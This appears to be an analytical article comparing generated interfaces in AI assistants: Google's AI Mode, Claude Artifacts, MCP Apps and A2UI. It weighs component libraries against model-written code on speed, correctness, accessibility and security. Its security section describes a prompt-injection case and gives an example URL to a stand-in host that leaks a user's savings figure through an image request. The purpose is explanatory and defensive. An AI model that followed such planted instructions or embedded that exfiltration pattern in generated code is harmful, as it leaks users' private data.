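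Pro and Ultra subscribers can choose stronger models in AI Mode. Gemini 4 Carbon arrived in early November and Gemini 4 Neon on December 3 (Schwartz, 2026, *Google AI Mode Gets Gemini 4 Neon For Subscribers*). Google's menu offers Hydrogen, the default, for ordinary questions, Neon for harder ones and Carbon for the hardest (Faisal, 2026, *Google Brings Gemini 4 Neon to Search AI Mode*). The stronger models may well produce better simulations, given how much the model mattered in the research system, but Google promoted Neon in Search for its quick, clear answers to hard questions, not for its interfaces.

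It's less clear how far the tools now extend beyond English. Sood writes that the improvements, including interactive tools, are coming to every language that AI Mode supports. In the summary of Google's announcement in Newsroom America's *Google Brings Gemini 4 Hydrogen to Search Worldwide* (2026), only the model's better understanding of language extends to all of them. Someone searching in Portuguese can expect a better answer and probably a generated tool too, but only Sood's reading supports expecting the tool.

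### Whether generation has become faster

Google says the custom tools now arrive "at the speed of Search", according to Newsroom America's summary, but the claim includes no figure. Google's wording is a poor guide to speed. In November 2025, Leviathan and colleagues wrote that AI Mode could "instantly build" an interface, but in the same announcement they acknowledged waits of a minute or more.

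In the research paper, Leviathan and colleagues give a more precise time of up to a minute or two, and say that streaming roughly halves the wait by letting people start on a partly finished page. That still leaves 30 to 60 seconds. The early instructions also tell the model to hold back its JavaScript until the browser has loaded the rest of the page, so at first people could probably read and scroll but not use the controls.

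Most of the wait comes from the amount of text the model has to write. If a full page is 10,000 tokens long and the model produces 150 tokens a second, writing it takes about 67 seconds, plus any time for planning and searches. Describing a layout of ready-made parts in 750 tokens would take 5 seconds.

The researchers also suggest making more use of speculative decoding, a technique three of them published in 2022. A small, fast model drafts the next few tokens, and the large model checks them all at once, which is faster than writing them one by one. Web code should suit this well because much of it is repetitive and easy to guess.

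Search has probably become faster since November 2025. Google replaced Gemini 3 Pro with models meant to be quick and cheap, and it now talks of assembling components. A feature that takes a minute would also be hard to put on a results page, where people expect an answer almost at once. The gain is likely to be largest for tables and visual layouts. A simulation coded from scratch still needs a lot of tokens, and Google hasn't said how long one takes to generate.

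## Other approaches: lasting artifacts and interfaces supplied by apps

OpenAI's Intelligent UI and Google's generated pages mostly serve one question at a time. Anthropic's Claude also draws temporary visuals, but its older and larger feature, Artifacts, is meant for generated tools that users keep. The designers of the MCP Apps standard believe instead that a service that owns the data, such as a restaurant's booking system, should supply its own interface and the assistant should only display it.

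### Artifacts: tools to keep

Keeping a tool is most useful when somebody uses it repeatedly. If a household recorded its spending every Sunday and an assistant generated a new tracker each time, it would use 52 trackers a year. Each could contain new mistakes, and none would include the previous week's entries. A lasting tracker only has to be made correctly once, and it keeps any corrections. Other people can use it too. Anthropic's *What are artifacts and how do I use them?* defines an artifact as anything Claude makes "that you'd put in front of someone".

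Claude makes an artifact when the user asks for one, or on its own when the content is substantial (typically over 15 lines), makes sense without the conversation, and is something the user will probably edit or return to. A spending tracker should become an artifact, while a short formula stays in the reply. Claude writes the code, and the artifact opens in a window beside the conversation. On a phone, users view it in the app's Artifacts tab.

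Users can also start from templates. According to Anthropic's *Release notes*, designs, slides and documents became available in any conversation on September 16, 2026. Another template builds dashboards from a company's data, and each chart shows the database query behind it and when it was last refreshed. This is a good safeguard for people who can read a query, because they can check where a suspicious figure came from.

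Users can revise an artifact by asking Claude for a change, and they can directly edit one made from a template. In a document, they can also highlight a passage and type a request about it. Editing an earlier message creates a second version of the conversation with its own artifacts, so users can try another design without losing the first. If an artifact reports an error, users can click a button to send the details to Claude, though Anthropic doesn't promise that the repair will work. Users have to catch mistakes that don't produce an error, such as a tracker adding up the wrong column.

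Claude saves every artifact to the Artifacts tab, where the user can find it from any conversation. People's entries in a tool need separate storage, which can be personal, as in a diary, or shared, as in a game's leaderboard. The limit is 100 MB or 25,000 records. If the household saves ten purchases a day as separate records, it will reach 25,000 in almost seven years. Artifacts can also connect to apps such as Slack and Google Calendar, or call Claude, so a quiz could give each player new questions.

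| Feature | Free | Pro, Max, Ultra | Team, Enterprise |
|---|---|---|---|
| Make artifacts in a chat | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Document, slide and design templates | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Data template | No | Yes | Yes |
| Spreadsheets and whiteboards (beta) | No | Yes | Yes, but off by default on Enterprise |
| Animations (beta) | No | No | Yes, but off by default on Enterprise |
| Store entries, connect apps | No | Yes | Yes |
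| Share with anyone who has the link | No | Yes | Only if an owner allows it |

Free users can make a tracker, but it can't store their entries and they can't share a link to it. They used to be able to share more freely. Willison (2024) noted on July 9, 2024 that users could now publish artifacts and remix other people's. Free users can still publish artifacts they made in chats before September 16, 2026, but not newer ones.

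Sharing is also limited on personal paid plans. According to Anthropic's *Share artifacts*, someone with only the link can read the saved entries after signing in to Claude, but can't change them or use features that rely on Claude or connected apps. On a Pro plan, this applies to everyone except the owner. If three flatmates open the owner's expense tracker through a link, they can see what they owe but can't add the electricity bill. The owner can invite them by email with permission to edit, but Anthropic doesn't make clear whether that permission lets them change the saved entries.

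Anthropic still promises on its main help page that people can share, at no cost, tools that call Claude, "whether your artifact helps 10 people or 10,000". That matches the rules for older artifacts but is probably out of date for new ones on personal plans. Colleagues on a company plan do get the full tool, so artifacts are more useful at work than among friends.

An artifact also lasts only as long as Anthropic supports it. The company replaced the original kind of chat artifact a little over two years after launching it. The old ones still work, but unpublishing one permanently deletes its stored data. Artifacts made before August 19, 2026 in Cowork, Claude's mode for longer tasks, also still work, but users can't edit them in place. Anyone who depends on a generated tool should probably keep a separate copy of its data.

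### Visuals inside Claude's replies

Since March 2026 Claude has also drawn interactive visuals inside its replies, as ChatGPT now does. Anthropic's *Custom visuals in chat and Cowork* compares them to a whiteboard sketch. Claude writes each one from scratch in HTML, so they are closer to Google's generated pages than to OpenAI's component library, though much smaller than a full page.

Anthropic's *Custom visuals* includes an example for a charity planning a fundraising campaign. The user types a goal, and Claude draws a pyramid showing how many gifts of each size the campaign needs and how many likely donors it must approach. Dragging the goal redraws the pyramid. The number of likely donors depends heavily on the assumed share who will give, so a fundraiser would need to check that assumption before relying on the pyramid. Ten gifts require approaching 40 people if one in four gives, but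 80 if one in eight does.

In an ordinary chat, clicking part of a visual can send Claude a follow-up question. For example, clicking the third quarter in a sales chart can prompt Claude to elaborate on that quarter. This partly solves the problem of the model not receiving what the user does on the screen, at least for clicks that send a message.

These visuals disappear by default, but users can download them or select "Save as artifact". This makes sense because people often can't tell whether a tool is worth keeping until they try it. The feature was still in beta in September, and the visuals didn't appear in Claude's phone apps. Those apps have been able to show interactive interfaces from other companies since March 25.

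### Letting the service supply the interface

A restaurant's booking system holds the current list of free tables and the rules about deposits and large parties. A booking form generated by a model may leave out a field the restaurant requires. The restaurant can instead design the form once, test it and take responsibility for it. It can also update the form while the user is looking at it, whereas a generated form may show only the tables that were free when the model wrote it.

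The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting AI models to outside data and tools. MCP Apps, its first official extension, lets a service supply a web page to display a tool's results. Model Context Protocol (2026), the project's launch announcement, argues for this approach using the example of a database that returns hundreds of rows. In a text conversation, each sort or filter needs another prompt, but in the service's own table the user can click a column. The announcement's example of a server monitor is a better argument for service-supplied interfaces, because a generated table could also sort and filter rows, whereas the monitor's display has to keep changing as new measurements arrive.

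Before the standard, developers had to adapt their interfaces to each host. OpenAI had its Apps SDK, a kit for building apps that run inside ChatGPT, and two independent developers, Ido Salomon and Liad Yosef, had created a similar system called MCP-UI. In November 2025, maintainers at OpenAI and Anthropic joined Salomon and Yosef in proposing a common method, as Model Context Protocol (2025) announced. The method became official on January 26, 2026.

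OpenAI's *Add UI to your MCP server* now tells developers to start with MCP Apps, though the Apps SDK's older commands still work. A plugin's panel in ChatGPT is therefore a web page from the outside service, shown in a restricted frame. OpenAI keeps some functions outside the shared standard, including its payment sheet, file handling and saving a panel's state. A developer who relies on these has to write an alternative for Claude.

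### A table for two through MCP Apps

In an example from Google's *Introducing A2UI* (2025), a user wants a table for two at 7 p.m. tomorrow, but the restaurant has tables only every half hour from 5:00 to 6:00 and from 8:30 to 10:00. A text-only assistant needs four exchanges to list these times. The example is a little unfair to text, because a competent assistant would offer 6:00 and 8:30 in its first reply. A form still helps the user see all seven times and choose one without typing.

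With MCP Apps, the booking would work roughly as follows. The tool names are invented, but the sequence follows Model Context Protocol's *MCP Apps Overview*.

1. When the host connects to the restaurant's server, the server sends a list of tools. The entry for `find_table` includes the address of a web page, which the host can download and inspect in advance.
2. The model calls `find_table` with the date, the time and a party of two.
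3. The host opens the page in a sandboxed frame. The page sends a `ui/initialize` message, and the host replies with details such as the user's language, time zone and available screen space.
4. The host passes the search details and the results to the page. The results include text for the model and can include fuller data for the page, such as a photo of each table.
5. The page shows the seven times, and the user taps 8:30 and then "Book".
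6. The page sends the host a request to call `book_table`. The host can ask for the user's approval before it forwards the request.
7. The restaurant's server checks that the table is still free and saves the booking. The page displays the confirmation.
8. The page sends a `ui/update-model-context` message, so the model has the new time.

A developer can easily forget the last message. Without it, a user who asks "when should I leave home?" may get an answer based on 7 p.m.

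The restaurant can also hide `book_table` from the model and let only its page call the tool. The model then can't book a table by mistake, but a user who types "just take the 8:30" still has to tap the button. If the host can't show the page, the tools still work and return text, but the restaurant would have to let the model make the booking.

The model is more useful for choosing what to display. OpenAI advises developers to provide one tool that finds data and another that draws the panel. In its example, a property service can search by city and price but not by school zone. The model runs a broad search, works out which homes are in the right zone, and sends only those to the panel. The user then sees them in a tested map and listings.

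### How much ChatGPT controls

The restaurant designs its own page within limits set by OpenAI. OpenAI's *UI guidelines* tell developers to use the device's standard fonts, leave backgrounds and text colours alone, and put no more than two main buttons on a card. ChatGPT adds the restaurant's name and logo. Cards within the conversation must not contain tabs, although OpenAI's own bicycle diagram has five. More complex displays, such as a map or a long menu, can fill the screen.

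OpenAI also limits what the restaurant can sell through ChatGPT, even if the restaurant owns the data and the interface. It currently approves purchases through plugins only for physical goods, unless it has given the developer special permission. A table deposit probably doesn't qualify, so a restaurant that requires one might have to finish the booking elsewhere.

### The same table through A2UI

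With Google's A2UI, the restaurant sends a description of the form and the host builds it. The restaurant runs an agent, a program in which a model carries out tasks, and the agent may use only components from the host's catalogue. Wang and Tian (2026), in *Developer's guide to Gemini Enterprise and A2UI integration*, explain how this works in Google's workplace assistant, using a restaurant finder as their example. With the message names from A2UI's *v1.0 Protocol Specification* (2025), the booking would go like this:

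1. The host sends the restaurant's agent the user's request and its catalogue of components.
2. The agent finds the seven free times and judges that a form would work better than text.
3. It sends `createSurface`, which opens a space for the form.
4. It sends `updateComponents`, which lists a heading, a choice of times and a button.
5. It sends `updateDataModel`, which supplies the date and any starting values.
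6. The host checks the components against its catalogue and draws them in its own style.
7. The user selects 8:30 and presses "Confirm". The host sends the agent an event named `confirm_booking` with the chosen time.
8. The agent books the table and sends another `updateComponents` message to show the confirmation.

Here are simplified descriptions of the choice and the button, with only two of the times:

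```
{"id": "time", "component": "ChoicePicker",
 "variant": "mutuallyExclusive",
 "options": [{"label": "6:00", "value": "18:00"},
             {"label": "8:30", "value": "20:30"}],
 "value": {"@path": "/booking/time"}}

{"id": "confirm", "component": "Button", "child": "confirm_label",
 "action": {"event": {"name": "confirm_booking",
   "context": {"time": {"@path": "/booking/time"}}}}}
```

Both refer to `/booking/time`, where the form keeps the selected time. When the user presses the button, the host reads the value there and includes it in the event. The description contains no fonts, colours or program code. Simple checks, such as requiring ten digits in a phone number, can run on the user's device, but only through functions already in the catalogue.

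If the agent stored the options as separate data, it can update the available times when someone else takes the 8:30 table, without resending the whole form. Wang and Tian write that in May 2026 Gemini Enterprise still used an older pattern, with the data written into each component.

### Who controls the booking

| | MCP Apps | A2UI |
|---|---|---|
| Layout | The restaurant's designers | The restaurant's agent, using the host's components |
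| Fonts, colours and buttons | The restaurant, within the host's rules | The host |
| Free tables and saved bookings | The restaurant | The restaurant |
| Pressing "Book" or "Confirm" | The restaurant's page requests a tool call, which the host can block | The host sends an event to the restaurant's agent |

The restaurant keeps its data and makes the final booking under both systems, so they differ mainly in who controls the appearance. Google acknowledges that A2UI gives the host more control over styling and the agent less. Version 1.0 goes further than earlier versions by rejecting a new form that includes the agent's own theme colours.

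This gives users some consistency. Someone who has enlarged the text in the host app should see a larger booking form too, and the specification requires hosts to pass component labels to screen readers. With MCP Apps, the restaurant has to make its own page accessible. Google also says web frames often clash with the app around them. MCP Apps reduces this by giving each page the host's colours and fonts, but the restaurant still has to use them.

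MCP Apps is better for unusual interfaces. For example, a restaurant can put a floor plan in its page so that guests can choose a table, and the same page can work in several hosts. With A2UI, each host would first need a floor-plan component in its catalogue. A2UI suits standard tasks such as picking a date, where a familiar control is probably more useful to the guest than the restaurant's branding.

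A2UI also lets the agent generate more of the interface. The agent can compose a new form for each request or fill in a fixed template, whereas an MCP Apps page is normally finished before the user asks for anything.

The two systems can work together, since A2UI messages can travel over MCP. Google's products also mix native components and web frames. The map in Wang and Tian's restaurant finder is an embedded Google Maps page, though it looks like another component in the chat. A Google Cloud event listing covers A2UI and MCP Apps together and includes Google Search among the products this work supports. That fits with Search assembling some answers from components, although the listing doesn't specify which technology Search uses.

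### Which assistants support them

MCP Apps had wider public support at launch. Claude displayed the pages on the web and desktop, and ChatGPT was due to follow that week. Goose, an assistant from the payments company Block, already supported them, as did a preview edition of Visual Studio Code, Microsoft's code editor. Harald Kirschner, a product manager at Microsoft, said in the Model Context Protocol announcement that the pages help when users need to decide, select or explore something. Amazon's cloud division, the software company JetBrains and Google's Antigravity team expressed interest but hadn't yet added the feature.

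A2UI is newer as a public format. Google released version 0.8 in December 2025 and version 0.9 in April 2026, and version 1.0 is now current. Each version changed how agents write their messages, so a restaurant may have to support more than one. Wang and Tian's sample agent already produces two patterns and picks the one the host can display. Developers can avoid some of this work by using a toolkit such as Genkit, which sends version 1.0 messages by default, according to Genkit's *Generative UI (A2UI)*.

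## Ready-made components or free code: what each can show, and where

The table compares the products as of early December 2026.

| | Intelligent UI | Gemini app | Google Search | Artifacts | App-supplied interfaces |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| What appears | Text with native components | Coded pages and simulations, or a magazine-style layout | Visual layouts, tables and tools | Documents, pages and tools | A web page (MCP Apps) or a form the host draws (A2UI) |
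| Who designed the parts | OpenAI | The model for coded pages, probably Google for the layout | Probably Google for some and the model for others | Claude, sometimes starting from a template | The outside company, or the host with A2UI |
| Where | ChatGPT's Chat tab | The Gemini conversation | AI Mode and AI Overviews | A window beside the chat, and the Artifacts tab | Inside the host's conversation |
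| Who triggers it | The model, or the user by asking | The user through a menu or prompt, or the model | The model, or the user by asking in AI Mode | The user, or Claude for substantial content | The model, by calling the service |
| What it saves | Checklist ticks, within one chat | Probably no entries in coded pages | Trackers and dashboards, but probably not one-off tools | The artifact, plus entries on paid plans | Whatever the service records, such as a booking |
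| Who has access | Free and paid plans, except at the Pro level | Personal accounts, with simulations also in Workspace | Everyone using AI Mode in English, with AI Overviews added since August | All plans, with fewer features on the free one | Users of hosts that support the service |

Google has teams on both sides of the dispute between components and free code. Its researchers wrote the strongest case for free code, while another team created A2UI because it considered running code written by a model a significant security risk.

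### How far a fixed library stretches

A component library can show more than its size suggests. If it has 30 components and an answer stacks five of them, there are about 24 million (30⁵) possible arrangements, even before the model adds labels or data. That is plenty for phone comparisons, recipes and road trips. But the library cannot show behaviour that nobody built into its components, such as Google's gravity simulation.

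Its designers could add a simulation component that accepts equations as settings. But a component that accepts any equations and rules is running a program, even if that program is written as labelled values. Google wanted A2UI to be "safe like data, but expressive like code". These aims conflict beyond a certain point, because a format that can express every simulation can also express one that is wrong or never finishes.

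The problem can arise with ordinary requests. Suppose someone has $5,000 in savings, will add $200 at the end of each month, and expects to earn 5% a year for 20 years. They want to see the final balance and a slider for each of the four numbers. With free code, the model writes the sliders and the formula. With components, as with the loan slider, the library needs either a finished calculator or a format that lets the model write the formula. Otherwise the app could have a server calculate each new balance, but the user would have to wait for the network after every slider movement.

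Calculating all the answers in advance isn't practical. With only 20 positions on each slider, there would be 160,000 of them.

Developers can extend a library to suit their users. *shinygenui* (Xiao, 2026) describes a small package that lets them do this in Shiny, a toolkit for making web apps in the programming language R. The developer decides which components the model may use and what settings each one accepts. A pension company could add its own tested calculator and cover most of what its customers ask. This works well for an assistant with a narrow job. Free code is more valuable in ChatGPT and Google Search, which receive questions about everything, so their libraries will always lack something.

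### Phones, results pages and other hosts

Ready-made components probably make phones easier to support. Unlike Intelligent UI, Google's dynamic view and Claude's coded visuals both lacked phone support for months after launch. But Claude's phone apps could already show other companies' web pages, so free code can run on a phone, and Anthropic may just have had other priorities.

Other software can also read a component description more easily than a page of code. Google points out that an agent coordinating several others can interpret the A2UI messages they send. An assistant that receives a savings form from a bank's agent could therefore tell the user what information the form requires. With a coded page, the assistant would have to work this out from the code or a screenshot.

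A finished page from an outside company doesn't behave the same everywhere either. ChatGPT lets such a page request a modal, a window the user must deal with before returning to what is underneath, but other hosts may not. OpenAI tells developers to test for the feature instead of checking the host's name, and to provide an alternative. In its sample code, the alternative is a line of text saying that the host doesn't support modals.

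### Two seconds or forty

The wait depends mostly on how much the model has to write. If the savings calculator takes 200 tokens as a component description and 4,000 as page code, a model that writes 100 tokens a second needs 2 seconds for the description and 40 for the page. These numbers are illustrative, and a real page could be several times shorter or longer.

The estimate leaves out time for thinking and searching, which both methods may need. If the model first spends 10 seconds looking up current savings rates, the totals become 12 and 50 seconds. The difference is still 38 seconds, but the page now takes about four times as long instead of twenty times.

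The gap can widen again when the user asks for a change. Google designed A2UI as a flat list in which every component has its own name, so the model can replace one without repeating the rest. If the user wants the term in months, the model would need 0.3 seconds to write a new 30-token description of the slider. Google's research system has to rewrite its whole page for a change like this. Free code doesn't inherently require that, since programming assistants often edit only a few lines of a long file.

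Component descriptions can also get shorter. OpenUI, an open standard for generated interfaces, has a compact language that its developers say uses up to 67% fewer tokens than JSON. At best, this would cut the 200-token description to 66 tokens and save 1.3 seconds. The saving is useful to a service that answers millions of questions, but few users would notice it.

The best reply from the free-code side is that models keep getting faster. At 1,000 tokens a second, the page would take 4 seconds and the description 0.2. The ratio is the same, but most people would accept a 4-second wait for a tool they wanted, though it might still be too long for a search results page. Component systems can use faster models too. OpenUI's *Introducing OUI-1* presents a model built on DiffusionGemma, which gains speed by working on many tokens at once instead of writing them strictly in order. Even so, speed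 is probably the component library's least durable advantage, because speeding up a 2-second answer saves much less time than speeding up a 40-second one.

### A savings calculator that is $3,150 short

With monthly compounding, the final balance is:

B = P(1 + i)ⁿ + D × ((1 + i)ⁿ − 1) / i

P is the starting sum of $5,000, D is the monthly deposit of $200, i is the monthly interest rate of 0.05/12, and n is the number of months, 240. The starting sum grows to about $13,563 and the deposits to about $82,207, for a total of about $95,770.

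A program can get the same result by updating the balance 240 times. In JavaScript, each update is:

```
balance = balance * (1 + 0.05 / 12) + 200
```

Now suppose the model compounds once a year instead, and writes this line to run 20 times:

```
balance = balance * 1.05 + 2400
```

The result is about $92,620, or $3,150 too little. Most of the shortfall arises because the yearly version treats each year's $2,400 in deposits as arriving all at once on the last day of the year, so January's deposit earns nothing until the following January.

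The user can't see this mistake on the screen. Both lines are valid code, so the browser reports no error. The balance rises when the user increases the rate or the deposit, as it should. Even a sensible test, such as setting the interest rate to zero, can miss the mistake, because both versions then give $53,000, the total paid in.

A user can find the error by setting the term to one year and checking the arithmetic, but someone able to do that probably doesn't need the calculator. The correct balance after a year is about $7,712, and the faulty tool shows $7,650. That includes $250 of interest, which is exactly 5% of the original $5,000, so the year's deposits have earned nothing.

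The correct balance also depends on what the 5% means and when the saver makes deposits. Banks often advertise an annual yield that already includes monthly compounding. If the 5% is such a yield, the balance is about $94,430. If it is an ordinary yearly rate and the saver deposits the money at the start of each month, the balance is about $96,110. A good calculator should therefore display its assumptions beside the result, however the model built it.

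### Which of these errors a library prevents

A component library is very good at preventing broken layouts. Programmers have already tested a component such as a slider, so it moves, its label doesn't cover the number, and it fits on a phone screen. The model doesn't write any JavaScript, so it can't make a typing error in it.

The library can also reject some bad settings. Xiao's package checks the values the model supplies before drawing a component. Suppose a savings calculator takes the interest rate as a fraction, such as 0.05, and the model writes 5. Without a check, the tool would apply a rate of 500% a year. A rule that rates must be between 0 and 0.3 would catch the mistake. A range like this wouldn't catch a monthly deposit of $250 when the user had asked for $200, since both are reasonable deposits.

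The library prevents the compounding error if it supplies a finished, tested savings calculator with the formula built in. If the library supplies only the sliders and the model writes the formula, the user still gets the same $92,620. A mistake in a shared calculator would affect everyone who used it, but its developers would probably hear about it and would have to fix it only once. When a model writes a new calculator for each person, nobody else sees the mistakes in that calculator.

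Models can also fail at using components. OpenUI's OUI-1 scored 71.7% on the project's Generative UI Benchmark, 5.5 times its base model's score, which implies that the base model scored about 13%. The developers trained OUI-1 first on examples, then on its own outputs, and finally across 27 component libraries so that it could work with more than one. OUI-1 is small enough to fit on a single consumer graphics card, so its score doesn't predict how well GPT-6 uses OpenAI's library.

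The low starting score points to an advantage of free code. Models see enormous amounts of HTML and JavaScript in training, but they have to be taught a new component language. Leviathan and colleagues got their error-free sample of Gemini 3 pages without training the model on a special format. Together, the two results show that a component library isn't automatically more reliable, but they come from different tests and models of very different sizes, so they don't establish that pages are more reliable than components.

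Supporters of free code can also point to automatic repair. In Google's research system, small programs correct known coding mistakes. More generally, a model can write a checklist for the request, score its page against it, and revise the page until it passes. For the savings calculator, another program could move the sliders to random positions and compare each balance with a separately written calculation. This would catch the compounding error, but not if the same model wrote both calculations and misunderstood the 5% the same way both times. The extra work would also add to the wait.

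### Using the calculator without a mouse or a screen

Accessibility is where a good component library should have its clearest advantage. Someone who can't use a mouse needs to move the slider with the arrow keys, and a blind user's screen reader has to announce what the slider controls and its current value. A library can include all of this once. HTML's own slider also includes most of it, so a model writing free code can use that slider without writing those features itself. But if the model builds a more attractive slider out of plain boxes, it has to add the keyboard controls and give the slider a role, a hidden label that identifies the type of control to other software. *WebAccessVL* (2026), a study of automatic repair, explains that screen readers can't interpret the elements on a page without roles.

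Most research in this area judges pages against WCAG, the international Web Content Accessibility Guidelines. *Large Language Models for Web Accessibility* (2026), a systematic review of studies that use language models to find or fix accessibility problems, lists the violations reported in each study. Three studies reported videos without audio descriptions, two reported pages that didn't show keyboard users which control they had selected, and one reported forms that didn't identify errors. In a savings calculator with this last fault, a person might type "5%" into a box that accepts only numbers and get a meaningless result with no explanation.

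These counts show how many studies reported a problem, so they don't measure how often it occurs in generated pages. The reviewers also found few standalone systems and benchmarks, and concluded that the field hasn't settled on shared testing methods. Components are fairly likely to be more accessible than free code, but on this evidence it is too early to say by how much.

Automatic checkers can help free code catch up, but *AccessGuru* (2025), which uses one called Axe-Playwright, acknowledges that they miss semantic violations, where the required text is present but its meaning is wrong or useless. For example, a checker can confirm that the savings chart has a text description even if that description is just "chart", but a blind user needs something like "the balance grows from $5,000 to $95,770 over 20 years".

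Components don't solve this problem either, because the model still writes the words. Google says A2UI lets an interface inherit the host's accessibility features "perfectly". That may be true of text size and keyboard controls, but it can't be true of a form in which the agent has labelled two sliders "Amount".

Repair can go wrong as well. *WebAccessVL* uses a loop in which a checker looks for violations and a model corrects them, and its authors warn that a badly chosen colour can cause new violations of its own. Suppose the calculator contains a link that looks just like the black text around it. The model could make the link orange so that people notice it. WCAG measures contrast like this:

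contrast = (L₁ + 0.05) / (L₂ + 0.05)

L₁ is the brightness of the lighter colour and L₂ that of the darker one, each on a scale from 0 to 1. White has a brightness of 1 and standard web orange about 0.48, so orange text on white has a contrast of about 2, below the usual minimum of 4.5 for ordinary text. The repair has fixed one violation and created another, and underlining the link would have been better. Each attempt would also add 40 seconds if it meant rewriting a 4,000-token page at 100 tokens a second.

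A repair could even break the calculator while making it more accessible. *LLM Based Web Accessibility Repair* (2026) reports that too little is known about whether such repairs preserve layout and behaviour on realistic websites. The study itself examines only the structure of pages and doesn't test how people use them. A slider with a perfect label could pass this kind of test even if it no longer changed the balance.

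### Stolen data and slanted defaults

Free code carries the greater security risk because it can act on what the user types. The model may read web pages while it prepares the savings calculator, and one of them could contain hidden instructions meant for AI systems. If the model followed them, it might add code that loads an invisible picture from an address like this:

```
https://example.com/dot.png?savings=5000
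```

The picture is only a pretext for the request, which sends the savings figure from the user's browser to whoever owns the address. A sandbox that keeps the page away from the user's account doesn't necessarily stop this. The host also has to restrict which addresses the page may contact. With that restriction, a harmful page has few ways to send anything out, so free code can be reasonably safe if the host is careful.

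A component library keeps out the harmful code but doesn't prevent every version of the attack. If its picture component accepts any web address, an attacker could get the model to put something the user said earlier into the address, and the app would send it when loading the picture. An attacker could also get the model to combine a trusted text box and a trusted button into a request for the user's password. Google says only that A2UI's catalogue of approved components "helps you to reduce" the risk of interface injection.

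An interface can be manipulative even when no attacker is involved. A component library can leave out countdown timers and pre-ticked boxes. A model writing free code may copy these tricks unless its instructions forbid it, because many of the real shopping sites it learned from use them. Hosts can also impose some limits on outside companies. For example, ChatGPT controls modals, so an app's page in its frame has to send a request before it can open a window over the conversation.

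Starting values are harder to control. Suppose a company that sells investments supplies the savings calculator and sets the rate at 7% instead of 5%. The tool then shows about $124,380. That is roughly $28,600 more, a difference nine times as large as the compounding error, even though the arithmetic is correct. This can happen equally with components and free code. A library could at least require a source beside any rate the user didn't enter, and that rule would be easier to enforce in a 200-token description than in 4,000 tokens of code.

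### A test that could decide between them

A fair test would give the same model a large sample of real questions and have it answer each one twice, once with a component library and once in free code. The researchers would then need to measure at least these things:

- how many of the questions the library couldn't handle
- how long users waited before they could operate the first control
- how often the numbers were wrong, compared with a trusted calculation over many random inputs
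- how often people using only a keyboard or a screen reader could complete the task
- how often a planted instruction on a web page got private data out

The test would need a large sample. If one method produced wrong formulas in 2% of calculators and the other in 4%, researchers would need about 1,100 calculators of each kind for an 80% chance of detecting the difference at the usual 5% significance level. They would also have to repeat the test as models improved, because the results, especially those on speed, would soon be out of date.

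The share of questions the library can't handle may matter most for product design. If it were 5%, a product could use components by default and write code only for the rest. Under the earlier assumptions, the average wait would be about 4 seconds, and only one user in twenty would have to trust a program nobody had tested. If the share were 40%, the average wait would rise to about 17 seconds, and making free code faster and safer would be more worthwhile than adding components.

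## Whether people are better served by generated interfaces than by text

A generated interface takes longer to appear than a paragraph and can fail in more ways, so it needs to offer people some benefit over text. In the two main studies, raters clearly preferred generated interfaces to text. There is much less evidence that these interfaces help people finish tasks sooner, make better decisions or learn more, and several experiments found no difference.

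### Google's pages against text, search results and freelancers

Leviathan and colleagues compared their generated pages with four alternatives: a page that a freelance expert made for the prompt, the top Google Search result, a model's answer in formatted text, and a model's answer in plain text. They used two sets of prompts. For the first, they took a random sample of 100 everyday prompts from LMArena and removed eight that seemed nonsensical or sensitive, leaving 92. For the second, they picked 100 prompts themselves, mostly requests for information such as "History of tea" and "Which phone is the best?"

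Raters compared two results and chose one or neither. Two raters judged each pair, so each everyday percentage below comes from about 180 judgments. The two percentages in each comparison don't add up to 100 because the remaining judgments were neutral.

| Rival | Everyday prompts: page preferred | Everyday prompts: rival preferred | Researchers' prompts: page preferred | Researchers' prompts: rival preferred |
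|---|---|---|---|---|
| Expert-made page | 35.3% | 50.0% | 30.0% | 55.5% |
| Formatted text | 82.8% | 13.9% | 90.5% | 6.5% |
| Top search result | 90.0% | 6.7% | 73.5% | 19.0% |
| Plain text | 97.0% | 3.0% | 95.5% | 3.5% |

The paper's claim that generated pages are at least comparable to the experts' in half of cases includes ties. On the researchers' own prompts, the figure is 44.5%. The freelancers also worked from guidelines much like the model's, with instructions to put interactivity first and prefer visuals to text. Nobody wrote a careful text answer for comparison, so the study can't show how a good human explanation would have done.

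Raters preferred formatted text to plain text by 81.1% to 1.1% on everyday prompts. Headings, lists and tables add almost nothing to the wait, so an assistant can probably provide some of what people like about generated pages without writing code.

The generated page's lead over formatted text hardly depends on the researchers' prompts that favoured it. At least nine of their prompts ask outright for a game, a tool or a web page, such as "robot vs robot boxing game", which text can't provide. Even if the generated page won every judgment on those nine, it still beat formatted text about 90% of the time on the rest.

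The choice of prompts mattered more for errors. The two oldest Gemini models, which often failed on everyday prompts, failed on 0% and 1% of the researchers' set. A demonstration on well-chosen prompts can therefore make a system look far more reliable than it is in ordinary use. These figures appear to count coding failures, not factual errors.

Newer models also made better pages, even when the older ones already worked. On the Elo scale, a lead of d points corresponds to an expected score, with a tie counting as half a win, of:

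E = 1 / (1 + 10^(−d/400))

Gemini 3's pages scored 161 Elo points higher than Gemini 2.5 Pro's on the researchers' prompts, which corresponds to an expected win rate of about 72%, though neither model made any errors on those prompts.

Raters saw finished pages, so their ratings didn't account for the wait. Most people would probably wait a minute or two for a gallery of Van Gogh's paintings. The test set also includes a question about making pizza crust in an ordinary oven, and someone who is already cooking may well prefer to get a list of steps immediately.

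### Five rounds of revision, and where the 72% comes from

In a July 2026 paper in the Findings of ACL, Chen and colleagues tested a slower system that revises its own work. The model first specifies the user's goal and the main features. It then turns this specification into a structured representation of the page's views and component states, and finally writes the web code.

The model also writes scoring criteria for each question. When a user asks to understand quantum physics, one criterion is whether the simulation effectively demonstrates wave-particle duality. The model produces several candidate pages, scores each from 0 to 100, and uses the best one and its evaluation to write the next round. It stops when a page reaches 90 or after five rounds. Interactive elements have a weight of 0.15, so a page that scores 60 on them and 95 on everything else has a weighted average of 89.75,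 and the model tries again if it has rounds left.

Most of the benefit seems to come from this revision. Annotators preferred the full system by 78% to 17% over a version that made only one attempt and used a general marking scheme. Also replacing the structured representation with an ordinary description widened the margin only slightly, to 82% against 13%. The drawback is a wait of up to several minutes.

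For the comparison with chat, the researchers used Claude 3.7 to write 100 test queries in ten fields. Three annotators judged each pair of answers, and the majority view decided the result. All 428 annotators were in the United States, had degrees and used chatbots regularly. The researchers discarded the work of annotators who failed trap questions or whose comments contradicted their choices.

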